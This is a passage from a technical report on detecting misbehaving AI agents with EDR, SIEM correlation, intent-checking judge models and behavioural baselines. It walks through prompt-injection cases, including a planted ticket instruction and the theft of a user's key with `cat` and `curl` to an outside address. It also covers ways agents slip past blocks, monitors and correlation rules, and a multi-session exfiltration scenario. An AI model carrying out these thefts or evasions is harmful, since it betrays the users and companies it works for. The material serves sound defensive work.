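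Sophos says that some rules need tuning for known agents and others should keep firing. For the cases that Sophos and Fishbein describe, a reasonable division would be:

| Activity that set off a rule | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Desktop's signed installer matches a ransomware rule | Exempt this behaviour | The signature identifies the publisher, and installers normally replace files |
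| An agent's PowerShell formatting resembles disguised commands | Narrow the rule | The formatting does no harm by itself |
| A browser skill decrypts saved logins | Keep blocking | The agent can use a separate browser profile with its own logins |
| Codex downloads Python with `certutil` or `bitsadmin` | Keep blocking | The company can provide an approved source for software |
| Cursor puts a script in the startup folder | Keep blocking | The script would keep running after the agent's session ends |
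| Cursor copies a process's memory while debugging | Keep blocking | The memory may contain passwords |

Blocking harmless work disrupts developers, and the table is based on the assumption that they have another way to do the job. Without one, the agent is likely to look for its own way after the blocked command goes back to the model as a failed tool call, as in the Codex example. Reviewing repeated blocks from the same agent together helps analysts see what it was trying to achieve.

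Exemptions should be as specific as possible. On a Mac that Elastic examined, a process under Claude Code ran a command that prints the agent's own login token from the Keychain, where macOS stores passwords. Elastic notes that this is documented behaviour. In one of Fishbein's cases, an agent that needed one token wrote the entire Keychain to a temporary file. An exemption could cover only the agent's login token, and only when the signed agent requests it, so that a full export still raises an alert. Exempting the `security` program, which runs both commands, would hide the full export too.

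A process name alone isn't enough to justify an exemption, because anyone can name a program `claude`. The exemption should also require the publisher's signature and the expected path, and it should have an owner and an expiry date, like any other grant of access. One well-chosen change can remove a lot of noise. Fishbein found that a single detection at one customer produced 55 percent of all "critical" verdicts by flagging a Windows file-expansion tool that a developer's agent was using to set up a shell.

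### Elastic's case for rules about outcomes

Elastic argues that a trusted agent at the top of a process tree shouldn't excuse what happens further down. Its main example is an odd series of events it found on a developer's Mac in July 2026.

On 20 July, Elastic's endpoint product flagged VPN and tunnelling programs on the Mac as malicious, though it can also flag legitimate commercial tools this way. The next day, a Python script in a temporary folder contacted an analytics service. On 22 July, alerts about processes started by AI tools rose sharply.

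The main events occurred on 23 July, in Claude Code sessions with permission prompts turned off. A shell running under the agent repeatedly contacted a login page at a web address supplied by a free tunnel service. When the page responded, the shell sent a username and password and retrieved a spending summary. The session also used `cloudflared`, a tunnelling program, to expose a service on the laptop to the internet. It then installed LaunchAgents, macOS settings files that start programs automatically. One checked every 60 seconds that the tunnel still worked.

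This could be an attacker keeping remote access to the laptop, or a developer who wanted to check an advertising dashboard from elsewhere and asked the agent to set it up. Some of the status messages were in Russian, which can look sinister but doesn't show who was behind the activity. The tunnel services have both legitimate and criminal users. Elastic doesn't choose between the explanations, and recommends that analysts record both when the evidence supports both.

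Exempting Claude Code's process tree would have hidden the whole sequence. The alerts were useful even if the developer had asked for every step, because a password had gone to a public address and a private service on the laptop was reachable from the internet. Someone needed to check both. The main advantage of rules about outcomes is that a team can act on their alerts before it knows the agent's intent.

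Elastic's rules cover several such outcomes. "Persistence via GenAI Tool" fired when the session installed the LaunchAgents. "GenAI Process Connection to Unusual Domain" fires when an AI tool on macOS connects to a domain that hasn't appeared in the organisation's records before. It may catch an upload to an attacker's server, but it will also fire when an agent opens the documentation for a new software library.

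Hernández and Lo Prete write their rules on the same principle. A poisoned web page and a malicious MCP server may both lead an agent to read a file it shouldn't, and a rule about the file can catch either without identifying the attack. Their rules also cover the reverse case, where a process outside the agent's process tree opens the agent's configuration folder, which often contains API tokens.

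Developers also read credentials, open tunnels and install background programs, so these rules will still produce false positives. To limit these, Elastic treats ordinary child processes as context and looks for combinations of more serious alerts. Its rule "Elastic Defend Alerts from GenAI Utility or Descendant" (Elastic, 2026) searches the ancestry of each alert for a known AI tool. It discards nine named detections, groups the rest by machine and agent process, and raises a critical alert when a group contains at least two different detections.

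This reduces noise without exempting the agent, but it can miss a short attack. The discarded detections include those for persistence and credential access through AI tools. If reading Dana's key triggers one of these and the upload triggers one other rule, only one detection counts, so the combined alert doesn't fire. The search also covers only nine minutes at a time, so an agent that waits an hour between steps could avoid it. Because of these gaps, the individual alerts remain important.

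A team can also act before an agent does anything harmful. Elastic's *GenAI CLI Started with Unsafe Permission Bypass* detects flags that let the agent run commands or edit files without asking. Fishbein calls such sessions the main risk in Intezer's data, but they are also the largest source of false positives because developers use the flags for legitimate work. If company policy forbids the flags outside isolated environments, the team knows how to respond to an alert whatever the developer was doing. If a developer changes the same setting in a configuration file, the flag may not appear on the command line for the rule to detect.

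### Where the endpoint record stops

Some agents do most of their work where the laptop's EDR sensor can't record it. Anthropic's *Claude Cowork architecture overview* describes an agent whose sessions run in Anthropic's cloud by default. Existing desktop installations can still run sessions locally, but shell commands then run inside a virtual machine, which has its own operating system. Anthropic states that EDR tools can't observe activity in the cloud or in the virtual machine. They may record the desktop app opening a file for the agent, but not what a script in the virtual machine does with it.

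This complicates the common advice, which Fishbein also gives, to run agents in a container or virtual machine. On a Linux server, containers share the host's kernel, so a kernel sensor can still record them. On Mac and Windows laptops, containers usually run inside a Linux virtual machine, and the laptop's own sensor misses most of what happens inside it. Isolation is often still worthwhile, but the team needs a sensor inside the virtual machine or records from the harness.

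Remote tools leave a similar gap in endpoint monitoring. When the hidden instruction in ticket 4711 makes the agent copy another customer's ticket into its reply, the laptop's sensor records only a connection to the usual MCP server. The theft happens inside the ticketing system, so no rule about local files or unusual destinations would catch it.

Unmanaged machines have no EDR sensor. A contractor might run an agent on a personal laptop and connect it to the company's code repository with a valid account. The EDR console would show no alerts from that laptop, whatever the agent did. Security teams can find some of these machines by comparing the devices in sign-in records with those that report to the EDR system.

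Even on a managed laptop, the record lists Dana as the user for everything her agent does. Fishbein notes that suspicious activity without the user's knowledge used to suggest that an attacker had taken over the machine. Analysts now have to check first whether an agent was responsible. Lineage often shows this, but background programs can break it. On the Mac that Elastic examined, a tunnelling program first ran under a shell and later under `launchd`, the macOS process that starts background services, so its lineage no longer pointed to Claude Code.

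The endpoint record also lacks the reason for an action. Hernández and Lo Prete note that prompt injection takes place while the model processes text, which cannot be observed from the kernel. Vendors have started to connect endpoint records with the prompts behind them. In *SentinelOne's Chris Corde On Why Traditional EDR Is 'Flying Blind'* (Alspach, 2026), Corde, the security company's product chief, says that its new product links the user's first prompt to the actions that follow. He was promoting a product launched the week before, but endpoint records do lack this link. Microsoft has also added checks for prompt injection to its Defender endpoint software.

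## Recording what the agent was asked and checking its actions against it

Dana's request is in the agent record but not in the endpoint record or the ticketing system's log, so an analyst can't tell from those two whether her agent was carrying it out.

### Permission and purpose

In *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)*, Errico (2026) proposes a specification for software that checks agents' actions before they run. He distinguishes whether policy permits an action from whether the action makes sense given the user's request and what the agent has already done. When the hidden instruction in ticket 4711 makes the agent open another customer's ticket, policy permits the action, but it makes no sense for Dana's task. Conversely, if policy forbids agents to delete database records but the user has asked the agent to clean up their own test data, Errico would allow the deletion, perhaps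 after a person confirms it.

Intent validation deals with the second question. *When Actions Go Off-Task* (Ning, Jones and colleagues, 2026) defines it for agents that operate a computer through its screen. A judge compares one proposed action with the user's instruction, given the agent's earlier actions and what is on the screen. The action is aligned if it serves the user's instruction rather than one planted in the agent's surroundings, has no unauthorised or undesired consequences, and can reasonably be interpreted as contributing to the task, directly or indirectly. An inefficient or unsuccessful action can still be aligned.

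The second condition matters when there is no attacker. An agent that uploads Dana's key to a diagnostic service to investigate a failed login is trying to do what she asked, but she never agreed to the upload. A tool that looks only for hidden instructions would miss this because there are none.

"Intent" here means what the user wanted, as far as their words express it, so the judge doesn't have to work out the model's motives. The judge can be a person, a fixed rule or a second language model. One of Errico's example rules blocks email to outside addresses once the agent has read personal data. A fixed rule can't determine whether another customer's ticket is relevant to a login fault, so most of the systems below use a language model as the judge.

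A judge can check an agent's whole run or each step. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) gives the example of a cooking assistant asked for recipes. If the assistant queries the user's medical records, that action fails the step-level check, even if the run as a whole stays about food.

The verdict can also have more than two values. *MetaPermit* (2026), an access control system for agents, has a model grade each tool as directly fulfilling the request, necessary for it, merely supporting it, or misaligned. The middle grades are useful because agents take many steps that nobody explicitly requested, such as installing a library before running a test. If the software can't parse the model's answer, it treats the call as misaligned and high risk.

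### Ways to collect the agent record

| Method | What it captures | What it misses | Can it block? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harness logs | Prompts, permission decisions and tool results, depending on the settings | Redacted content, and what a script does after it starts | No |
| Hooks | Any step for which the vendor provides a hook | Other steps, and agents without hooks | Yes, if the harness waits for an answer |
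| Tool gateway | Calls to MCP servers and their results | Local commands and files, and usually the user's request | Yes |
| Local session files | Prompts, visible reasoning, tool calls and results | Whatever the harness doesn't save | No |
| Kernel probes joined to model traffic | Prompts, responses, processes, files and connections | Activity inside remote services | Not in AgentSight |

Records that an agent's own software keeps can be incomplete or altered.

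Hooks are programs that the harness runs at fixed points, for instance before each shell command. Elastic's *13 million tool calls* describes how the company used them to audit Cursor, the AI code editor, on its employees' machines. A script of about 280 lines recorded over 13 million events from more than 1,100 machines in two months. File reads outnumbered shell commands by roughly four to one. The agents connected to more than 300 different MCP servers, 86 percent of which had only one or two users. Before the audit, Elastic's list of servers included only those that people remembered to mention.

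For some hooks, Cursor waits for a response before it continues. Elastic's script approves the action first and writes the log entry afterwards, so a fault in the script can't hold up a developer. If a hook crashes, Cursor lets the action proceed by default. Errico's specification forbids this because an attacker could get past the check by making it crash. Elastic's choice makes sense for a script that only records actions, but a team that wants to block them should change the default.

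The hooks stayed inactive on each machine until someone restarted Cursor, although Elastic's deployment tools reported success. A team can catch this by running a harmless agent session on each type of machine and checking for the events it should generate.

An analyst can use Elastic's log to find a machine where an agent has suddenly read twenty credential files in an hour. But the log leaves out prompts and model responses, so the analyst can't use it to determine whether the agent's task required reading those files.

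Microsoft uses hooks to block activity as well as record it. The runtime protection in its Defender endpoint software, which Microsoft describes as a preview, receives the user's prompt, each tool call before it runs and each response afterwards. Administrators can choose whether it blocks suspicious activity or only raises an alert. The prompt, tool calls and responses are nearly all the data that intent validation needs, but Microsoft describes the scan as a search for prompt injection, not a test of whether actions fit the task. The runtime protection supports only Claude Code and GitHub Copilot CLI.

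A gateway is a server that sits between the agent and its tools and can refuse a call. Errico says the agent needs little modification because only the address of the tool server changes. Li and colleagues decided against gateways at Uber, arguing that gateways require changes to the agent software, don't work with streamed responses and capture only part of the context.

The two accounts can be reconciled. Redirecting the calls is simple, but sending the user's request along with them, which Errico also recommends, takes extra work. Without the request, a gateway would record the theft from the other customer's ticket as two ordinary ticket reads. It would record nothing when the agent reads Dana's key, because that call never leaves the laptop.

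### Linking a model's response to what happened on the machine

AgentSight, the research tool from Zheng and colleagues that links model traffic to operating system events, works without support from the harness. It attaches probes to the functions in encryption libraries, such as OpenSSL, that programs use to send and receive encrypted data. These probes copy the prompt before encryption and the response after decryption. Separate probes in the kernel record new processes, opened files and network connections.

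The tool uses three signals to match a response to the events it caused. For the theft of Dana's key, they would work like this:

- **Lineage:** the shell that ran `cat` is a descendant of the harness.
- **Time:** the shell opened the key file shortly after the model's response arrived. AgentSight uses a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Matching arguments:** the response contained the path of the key file, and so did the request to open it.

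Each signal has a weakness. A large build can start hundreds of processes that all descend from the agent. Two agents working in parallel may receive responses within the same half second. Arguments don't match if a script assembles the path only at run time. Zheng and colleagues write that the three signals together "definitively" establish causes, but their evidence is a handful of case studies, and they didn't count wrong or missing links. In their tests on three development tasks, each repeated three times, AgentSight slowed Claude Code by 0.4 to 4.9 percent.

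Errico argues that kernel monitoring alone can't establish the context of an action. The requests that reach the kernel don't include what the user asked for. Suppose an agent uploads the same log file to the same server twice, once because the user asked and once because it followed an instruction on a web page. The system calls are identical, so recording them in more detail wouldn't distinguish the two uploads.

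AgentSight gets the context from the model traffic, so it isn't a counterexample. Its second model also analyses the events only after they happen, too late to stop them.

Errico's specification therefore treats kernel monitoring as a backstop. A kernel monitor is harder for an agent to bypass than a hook, and it can enforce fixed prohibitions, such as a ban on connections to a known malicious server. But a vendor that uses only a kernel monitor can't claim compliance with the specification. Errico argues for this design without reporting measurements, and lists building a reliable classifier of intent as an open problem.

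### Uber's detection system

The largest published deployment is Uber's ADR (Agentic AI Detection and Response), which grew over more than ten months to cover more than 7,200 machines and 10,000 agent sessions a day. Its sensor runs on company MacBooks and reads the databases and session files that the coding agents Cursor, Claude Code and Cline save locally. It uses these to reconstruct the user's prompts, the agent's visible reasoning, the tool calls and their results. It also records which MCP servers and software packages the agent could use. Each run of the sensor takes about 0.2 seconds.

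A two-stage detector then examines the sessions. A language model screens them all and closes only those that are clearly harmless. A second model investigates the rest and can look up a tool's source code, a library of known attack techniques and the company's policies. Li and colleagues tested the detector with GPT-4o in the first stage and Claude Sonnet 4 in the second. The first stage settled 41 percent of the tasks, and the whole process averaged 18.5 seconds and 2.4 cents per task.

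The researchers also built ADR-Bench, a benchmark of 302 tasks that use 133 MCP servers. Of the tasks, 42 contain an attack and 260 are benign. They compared ADR with three existing detectors. ALRPHFS matches behaviour against known attack patterns, GuardAgent checks it against written policies, and Meta's LlamaFirewall combines a small classification model with fixed rules.

| Detector | Attacks detected, of 42 | False positives, of 260 |
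|---|---|---|
| ADR | 28 (67%) | 0 |
| ALRPHFS | 17 (40%) | 34 (13%) |
| GuardAgent | 9 (21%) | 30 (12%) |
| LlamaFirewall | 8 (19%) | 40 (15%) |

ADR clearly outperformed the other detectors, although its developers also wrote the benchmark and adapted those detectors to it. It detected all nine attacks that bypassed security controls or disrupted operations, but only one of the five that abused permissions. Five cases are too few for a reliable rate, but permission abuse is the category closest to the theft from the other customer's ticket.

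Li and colleagues also removed parts of the detector to measure what each contributed. Without access to tools' source code, it detected 57 percent of the attacks. Removing the company policies made almost no difference, which they explain by saying that most of the attacks were obvious without the policies. ADR-Bench may therefore measure how well a detector recognises attacks more than how well it spots permitted actions that don't fit the task.

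Removing the first stage raised detection to about 80 percent, but it also added two false positives and increased the bill by 29 percent. That stage was a quick screening meant to pass on anything doubtful, and it had evidently dismissed several attacks as harmless.

ADR raised no false alarms on 260 benign tasks, but at 95 percent confidence its true false-alarm rate could still be as high as about 1.15 percent, because a detector with that rate would have a 5 percent chance of getting through all 260 without one. At 10,000 sessions a day, nearly all of them benign, that rate would mean about 115 false alarms daily. The 1.15 percent limit also assumes that the benign tasks resemble everyday work at Uber, but GPT-4 generated some of them. On AgentDojo, a public benchmark for prompt injection, ADR detected all 38 attacks but flagged 3 of the 55 benign tasks, or 5.5 percent.

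In production, Uber's analysts judged 49 percent of the alerts they reviewed to be false positives. Another 17 percent correctly detected activity that wasn't malicious, mostly by the company's own security testers, and 34 percent were real problems. Many of the false positives came from long sessions in which an agent analysed a large codebase. Li and colleagues describe these as cautious referrals rather than the kind of error the benchmark measures, which is fair, but an analyst still had to read each one. The 49 percent is a share of alerts, not of sessions, so it can't be compared with the benchmark's false-positive rate.

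ADR's sensor runs once an hour, so its alerts come after the event. The most common genuine problem was exposed credentials, which had often left the company by the time an alert appeared. There were also too many of these alerts to review by hand.

Uber therefore added its prompt filter, which runs as a hook in Cursor and Claude Code and blocks likely secrets. It identifies them by matching text patterns and measuring how random a string looks, without using a language model. The hook flagged 212 different credentials, and 206 of them were real, a precision of 97.2 percent. The number it missed is unknown. The filter probably wouldn't have protected Dana's key either, because she never put the key in a prompt and the agent fetched it later.

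### Judging an action before it runs

Claude Code's auto mode validates intent before the agent acts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that people accept 93 percent of permission prompts, so a second model now makes most of these decisions. Harmless types of action, such as file reads and edits inside the project folder, skip the check. For everything else, the second model decides whether the user authorised the action or it is merely related to the user's goal.

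The judging model receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that they can't lead the judging model to a bad decision. Anthropic also removes tool results, because injected instructions arrive in them.

If Dana's agent reads her key with the built-in file reader, the read goes through unchecked. When the agent tries to upload the key, the judging model compares the upload command with the request to summarise a ticket, and it can find the mismatch without the ticket's text.

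Anthropic tested the system on three sets of actions. A fast first stage errs towards blocking, and a slower second stage reconsiders whatever the first flags.

| Test set | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| 10,000 tool calls from employees' real work | 8.5% of benign calls blocked | 0.4% of benign calls blocked |
| 52 real actions that went beyond what the user wanted | 6.6% missed | 17% missed |
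| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | 1.8% missed | 5.7% missed |

The 17 percent comes from only 52 cases, so the true figure could plausibly be anywhere from about 9 to 30 percent. The 0.4 percent is a rate per call, while ADR's figures are per task, and an ADR-Bench task averages 28.5 tool calls. If mistakes were independent, a session of that length would have roughly a one in ten chance of at least one wrong block.

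A wrong block does limited harm here because the agent receives the reason and can try another way. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code asks the user.

Many companies may already be using this check without choosing it. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* announced the new default for the Pro, Max, Ultra and Team plans in August 2026. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), by 12 November interactive sessions on every plan started in auto mode, but scripted runs still started in manual mode.

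Results for other judging models vary widely. Ning and colleagues had people label 2,264 actions by computer-use agents, 1,000 of them misaligned. Their method, running on GPT-5.1 Thinking, caught 77 percent of the misaligned actions, and its precision implies that it wrongly flagged about 7 percent of the aligned ones. InferAct, an earlier method, caught 96 percent running on Claude Sonnet 4.5 but also flagged about four in five of the aligned actions. Misaligned actions are much rarer in ordinary work than in this test, so a larger share of the flags would be mistaken.

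A judging model may also base its verdict on how alarming a command looks rather than on whether the user authorised it. *Same Operation, Different Permission* (2026) tests for this with pairs of cases that differ only in authorisation. Qwen3.5-9B judged both cases correctly in 4 of 24 pairs, the larger Qwen3.5-27B in 23, and a third model, Safeguard, in 20. Before relying on a judging model, a team can write a few pairs like this from its own work, for example the same deletion with and without a request for it.

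### Vague requests and changes of plan

Intent validation is easiest when the user has said exactly what they want. One of Anthropic's internal incidents began with a request to "clean up old branches" (separate lines of work in a code repository). The agent deleted branches on the shared server, though the user may have meant only those on their own machine. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the judging model identified the danger but treated weak evidence of consent as sufficient. A request to "clean up the PR", for example, doesn't authorise an agent to overwrite shared history, and neither does one earlier approval of something similar.

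Performance may be much worse when most requests are vague. besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* summarises an independent test that used deliberately ambiguous requests, such as cancelling a job or cleaning up files. Auto mode allowed 115 of the 142 actions it should have stopped and blocked 22 of the 111 that were fine. Some of the 115 were types of action that the judging model never checks. The exact figures deserve little weight because the summary is secondhand and another model produced the initial labels.

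Plans also change for good reasons. An agent investigating why a customer can't log in may start with the ticket, find an error code and move on to server logs that Dana never mentioned. Errico describes a similar sequence that ends badly. A user asks for help preparing for a client meeting, and the agent reads the client's account and emails. One email mentions a competitor's prices, so the agent looks up the competitor and eventually opens confidential strategy documents. Nobody has attacked the agent, and each step follows plausibly from the last.

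Errico suggests detecting such drift by measuring the "semantic distance" between the original request and each action. Software converts both into embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent meaning, and calculates 1 − cosine(embed(request), embed(action)). The result is near 0 when the two are similar and rises as they diverge.

This score seems too crude to rely on alone. Opening another customer's ticket is very similar in meaning to opening ticket 4711, so the theft would probably get a low score, while a legitimate search of the server logs might get a higher one. Errico doesn't propose a universal threshold and says that each deployment has to find its own.

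When the evidence is unclear, the specification allows a system to defer an action, or suspend it until more information arrives. Any later step that needs the result also has to wait, and if nobody resolves the question in time, the system refuses the action. For the login fault, the simplest resolution is to ask Dana whether the agent may read the server logs. Her answer then becomes part of the instruction for later checks. Asking too often would bring back the permission prompts that people approve without reading.

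Delegation can hide the original request. When Dana's summariser hands an attachment to a second agent, that agent receives the summariser's instruction in place of a user's message. If the summariser has already followed a hidden instruction, whatever it passes on will look authorised to a judge that checks only the second agent. Anthropic therefore checks the handoff, while Dana's words are still available for comparison. It checks again when the second agent returns its results, but then it only adds a warning.

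### Prompts contain private data

People put customer records, passwords and personal information into prompts, so an agent's records can be more sensitive than the systems they help to protect. Uber keeps its agent records for 13 months. Li and colleagues say the company removes secrets from them where it can and lets only security staff read them. Uber's legal, privacy and risk teams reviewed the system before deployment.

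Elastic's policy is to record commands, file paths and tool names, but not prompts, model responses or file contents. Only the small team that runs the system has full access. Elastic told employees what it would collect before the rollout began, and it reports no objections. However, commands can contain passwords, and each log entry also keeps the hook's original data. A team that copies the script should check what that data contains before promising to exclude the same content.

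Elastic's approach protects employees better, but it rules out intent validation from the stored log because the company hasn't kept the request to compare with the action. As a compromise, the company could run the check while the agent is working, when the prompt is available, and store only the action, the verdict and a short reason. Investigators would then have to rely on the judging model's verdict because they couldn't repeat the comparison. Keeping full prompts for a few days, and longer only for sessions that raised an alert, would give them a chance to repeat it.

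## Correlating agent events in the SIEM

A SIEM can collect the agent record along with logs from EDR, the ticketing system and the authorisation server. It converts these records to common fields, joins those that belong to the same activity, applies rules, ranks the alerts and passes them to an analyst. With agents, joining the records is often the hardest step because each system identifies the same activity differently.

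### What to collect

| Source | Events to send | Fields for joining |
|---|---|---|
| Harness or hooks | Requests or a verdict on them, tool calls, results, approvals | Agent, session, tool call, machine, process, time |
| EDR | Process starts, opened files, connections | Machine, process, parent process, user, time |
| Authorisation server | Tokens issued, refused and revoked | User, agent, token identifier, time |
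| MCP servers and remote services | Requests and their results | User, agent, token identifier, time |
| Agent register | Owner, purpose, approved tools | Agent |

The tool call identifier connects a request from the model to its result, and the session identifier groups all the calls from one conversation. To connect a session to the endpoint record, the SIEM needs the machine and the harness's process number. It also needs the time the process started, because operating systems reuse process numbers.

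A token identifier links the ticketing system's log to the token that the authorisation server issued. The standard field for this is `jti`, which would need to be added to the earlier example token for Dana's summariser. Logging the token itself instead would put a working credential in the SIEM.

Some remote services now record agents separately from users. Google's *AgentAttributionInfo* defines audit log fields for the type, ID and name of the agent that performed an action, along with its owner's email address. Microsoft includes an agent's ID and display name in its log of identity risks. An agent may have a different ID in each system, so the register should list all its IDs.

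Approval records are worth keeping even if a team has to cut its log volume. Microsoft rates tool-call volume as high and approval-decision volume as low for one of its own agents. An approval record also shows an analyst that a person accepted the action.

### Converting records to common fields

Elastic first stored the data from Cursor's hooks as it arrived, but the same command appeared in different places depending on the event type. Elastic then changed its script to copy the tool name, command, file path and MCP server into fixed fields. It still keeps the original data because agent vendors often change what their hooks send. The fixed fields in its example entry include the session and the machine but no process number, so an analyst would have to match the entry to the endpoint record by command and time.

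Two shared formats could save each company from inventing its own fields. OpenTelemetry is an open standard for telemetry from software, and the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF) is a common format for security events. Microsoft also has an agent event format for Sentinel, its SIEM. The main fields for joining records correspond roughly as follows:

| Identifier | OpenTelemetry | OCSF | Microsoft Sentinel |
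|---|---|---|---|
| Agent | `gen_ai.agent.id` | `message_context.service` | `SrcAgentId` |
| Session | `gen_ai.conversation.id` | `message_context.uid` | `EventSessionId` |
| Tool call | `gen_ai.tool.call.id` | None in `message_context` | No dedicated field |
| Machine | `host.id` | `device.uid` | `SrcFQDN` |
| Process | `process.pid` | `process.pid` | `ActingAppId` |

None of the three formats requires the session field in every event. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* requires the conversation ID only "when available". OCSF only recommends its equivalent, according to documentation from Tenzir, a security data company. Version 0.1.0 of Microsoft's Sentinel format makes the session, tool and user fields optional.

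The OpenTelemetry fields are also still changing. Greptime (2026), a database company, lists changes to the AI fields in every release from 1.37 to 1.41, including a new name for the model provider field. A rule that searches for the old name finds nothing and gives no error. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, reports that the project moved these fields to a separate repository in June 2026. On 21 August they still had "Development" status, and the repository had no official release.

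OCSF version 1.8.0, which AWS dates to 16 March 2026, added AI fields, including the model, the number of tokens and the session. OWASP's *AOS tracing with OCSF* extends an existing OCSF event type for API activity to record an agent's tool calls. OCSF already uses "agent" for monitoring software such as an EDR sensor, as lmodel's copy of the schema shows. An integration that puts an AI agent's name in a field meant for that software would list the AI agent among the company's security sensors.

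Products can follow a shared format and still produce events that can't be joined. *Standardize thread/caller correlation on AI OTel spans (map tags to gen_ai.conversation.id)*, a proposal from the web publishing project Drupal, describes how its AI modules identified conversations with their own tags. A later change introduced a new kind of tag that no existing tool could read. The proposed fix is to copy the value into `gen_ai.conversation.id`. The monitoring company Honeycomb notes that Claude Code already sets this field.

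Even in complete OpenTelemetry records, the agent fields identify the software that ran but not who authorised it or under what limits, as TinyFish points out. For that, the SIEM needs the delegation token's record, which must identify both Dana and the agent.

### A rule for the theft of Dana's key

With these fields in place, a rule can look for the steps of the theft in order:

A SIEM rule can raise an alert when three events happen in order within 10 minutes in the same agent session. First, a tool result brings in outside content (a ticket, an email or a web page). Then a process in the session opens a file on the list of secrets. Finally, a process in the session connects to an address that nobody in the company has contacted in the past 30 days.

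A process is in the session if it is the session's harness process,
or descends from that process on the same machine.
```

The records of the theft might look like this:

| Time | Record | Event | Session | Process |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 10:02:11 | Harness | Ticket 4711 arrives | a71f | 4120 |
| 10:02:40 | EDR | `cat` opens the key file | Not recorded | 4188, descended from 4120 |
| 10:03:05 | EDR | `curl` connects to 203.0.113.7 | Not recorded | 4203, descended from 4120 |

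The EDR sensor doesn't track sessions, but process 4120 appears in both records, so the SIEM can assign all three events to session a71f. The events span 54 seconds, and the rule fires.

The ten-minute window is a compromise, because a longer one catches slower attacks but also more coincidences, such as an agent that reads a web page, opens a settings file containing a password and then downloads a package from a new site. The rule should use the time when each event happened, not when it reached the SIEM. Uber's sensor collects agent sessions only once an hour, so a rule that searched by arrival time might never find all the steps within the same ten minutes.

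### When a key is missing or the session changes

If the harness log leaves out the process number, the SIEM has a ticket in session a71f and two endpoint events with no session, so the rule doesn't fire.

If a team loosened the rule to match any events by the same user on the same machine, the rule could mistake Dana's own use of her key for theft. When she logs in to a new server while her agent reads a ticket, `ssh` opens the key file and connects to an unfamiliar address, which matches the loosened rule. That rule would also mix up two agents working at once, as would the original rule if one harness process ran both sessions.

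If events lack the machine name, the SIEM could match process 4120 on Dana's laptop with process 4120 on someone else's. If the ticket read comes from the ticketing system's log and the laptop's clock is a minute slow, the key appears to have been opened before the ticket arrived, so the rule rejects the sequence.

A complete set of fields doesn't help when the attack spans several sessions. *Cross-Session Threats in AI Agents* (Azarafrooz, 2026) gives an example with six sessions. In the first, someone posing as an engineer asks an assistant which data sources it can access, and in the second asks it to describe the configuration files. The assistant reads a database configuration file in the third session and summarises it in the fourth. It encodes the summary in the fifth and sends it to an outside address in the sixth. The assistant therefore reads the secret three sessions before it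 makes the outgoing connection. There may also be no outside content in any of the sessions, because the attacker types the requests.

Grouping events by user over a week would bring the steps together, but it would also match a lot of ordinary work. Elastic notes that agents "constantly" read `.env` files, which often hold passwords, because the files contain connection settings. Over a week, many developers' agents would also read a web page and contact a new site.

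A more selective rule could link sessions by the data passed between them. For example, it could link a session that reads a secret and writes a file to another that reads that file before contacting a new address. The rule needs records of both file reads and writes. It fails if the information passes through an agent's stored memory in a provider's cloud, or if a person copies it between chats.

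The rule also misses the theft of the other customer's ticket, which involves neither a secret file nor a new address.

### How many events to expect

For a rough estimate, take a company with 10,000 agent sessions a day, about the number at Uber, and assume 20 tool calls in each. Help Net Security's *Sysdig AI Defense puts runtime guardrails on AI agents* reports an early figure from Sysdig, which sells the product, of about seven processes for every action in an agent's log. The company would then record:

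10,000 sessions × 20 tool calls × 7 processes = 1.4 million process events a day

That averages 16 a second. The 20 calls per task are an assumption, and Sysdig's ratio is a vendor figure that will vary with the work. At 28.5 calls per task, the average in Uber's benchmark, the total would be about 2 million. Opened files and network connections would add more.

Elastic's hooks produced far fewer events, about 213,000 a day from 1,100 machines, but they recorded the steps of the agent loop, not the underlying processes. A single shell command can still trigger several hooks.

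A SIEM can handle 1.4 million events a day, but false alerts are harder to manage. At that volume, a rule that wrongly fires on one process event in 10,000 would produce 140 false alerts a day. Searches can also be incomplete, because Elastic's query language returns at most 1,000 rows unless the analyst raises the limit. At 16 events a second, that covers about one minute of activity.

One way to reduce the volume is to attach process events to their tool call as they arrive, then store one summary for each call. This would leave 200,000 records a day for everyday searches. The full events can go to cheaper storage for a few weeks in case an investigator needs a detail the summary omitted.

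### Baselines built for people

A behavioural baseline describes what is normal for one account, such as its working hours, the systems it uses and how much data it reads. The SIEM scores new activity by how far it departs from that baseline, so it can flag an attack that no rule describes. *Enterprise AI needs a new model for behavioral intelligence*, a TechRadar article by the field security chief of Exabeam, which sells this kind of analysis, explains why agents are harder to baseline. An employee who logs in at 3 am may deserve a closer look, but an agent may legitimately work all night. An agent can also use dozens of services within seconds, and its permissions may grow as the company gives it more to do.

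Elastic suggests that if agents on a machine usually read about four credential files a day, twenty reads in an hour outside the working repository would deserve attention. If reads happened independently at that rate, twenty in an hour would be almost impossible by chance. But an agent asked to update the settings of twenty services may read all the files in one burst, so the count is weaker evidence than it appears.

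A change of task can make the baseline obsolete. Dana's coding agent may write tests on Monday and investigate a database on Tuesday. If it runs under her account, the baseline also mixes her habits with the agent's. A TechRadar article recommends a baseline for each agent, which is a sensible minimum. A team could also keep one for each type of task and restart it when the agent gets a new model or MCP server.

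A baseline works best for agents with narrow jobs. If the ticket summariser almost always opens one ticket per request, opening a second customer's ticket stands out, even though the action is permitted and involves no secret file. A baseline could therefore catch the theft that the correlation rule misses. It would be much less useful for an agent that investigates login faults and regularly opens a dozen tickets.

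Vendors now sell ready-made detections of this type. *What's New in New-Scale July 2026* (Chelmo, 2026) announced that Exabeam had reached 90 detections for agents. That number does not measure accuracy, so a buyer should run the detections silently on its own agents first.

### CSTM-Bench and attacks spread over sessions

The six-session example comes from CSTM-Bench, a benchmark that Azarafrooz built to test whether language models can detect such attacks. Its 54 synthetic scenarios include 26 attacks, 14 cases of ordinary work and 14 cases of harmless work that resembles an attack. One kind of lookalike is a long series of routine approvals that ends with a request to approve one more item. Each scenario includes a short policy for the agent, such as that a support agent may discuss orders but may not share credentials.

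Azarafrooz compared three detectors, all of them using Claude Sonnet 4.6:

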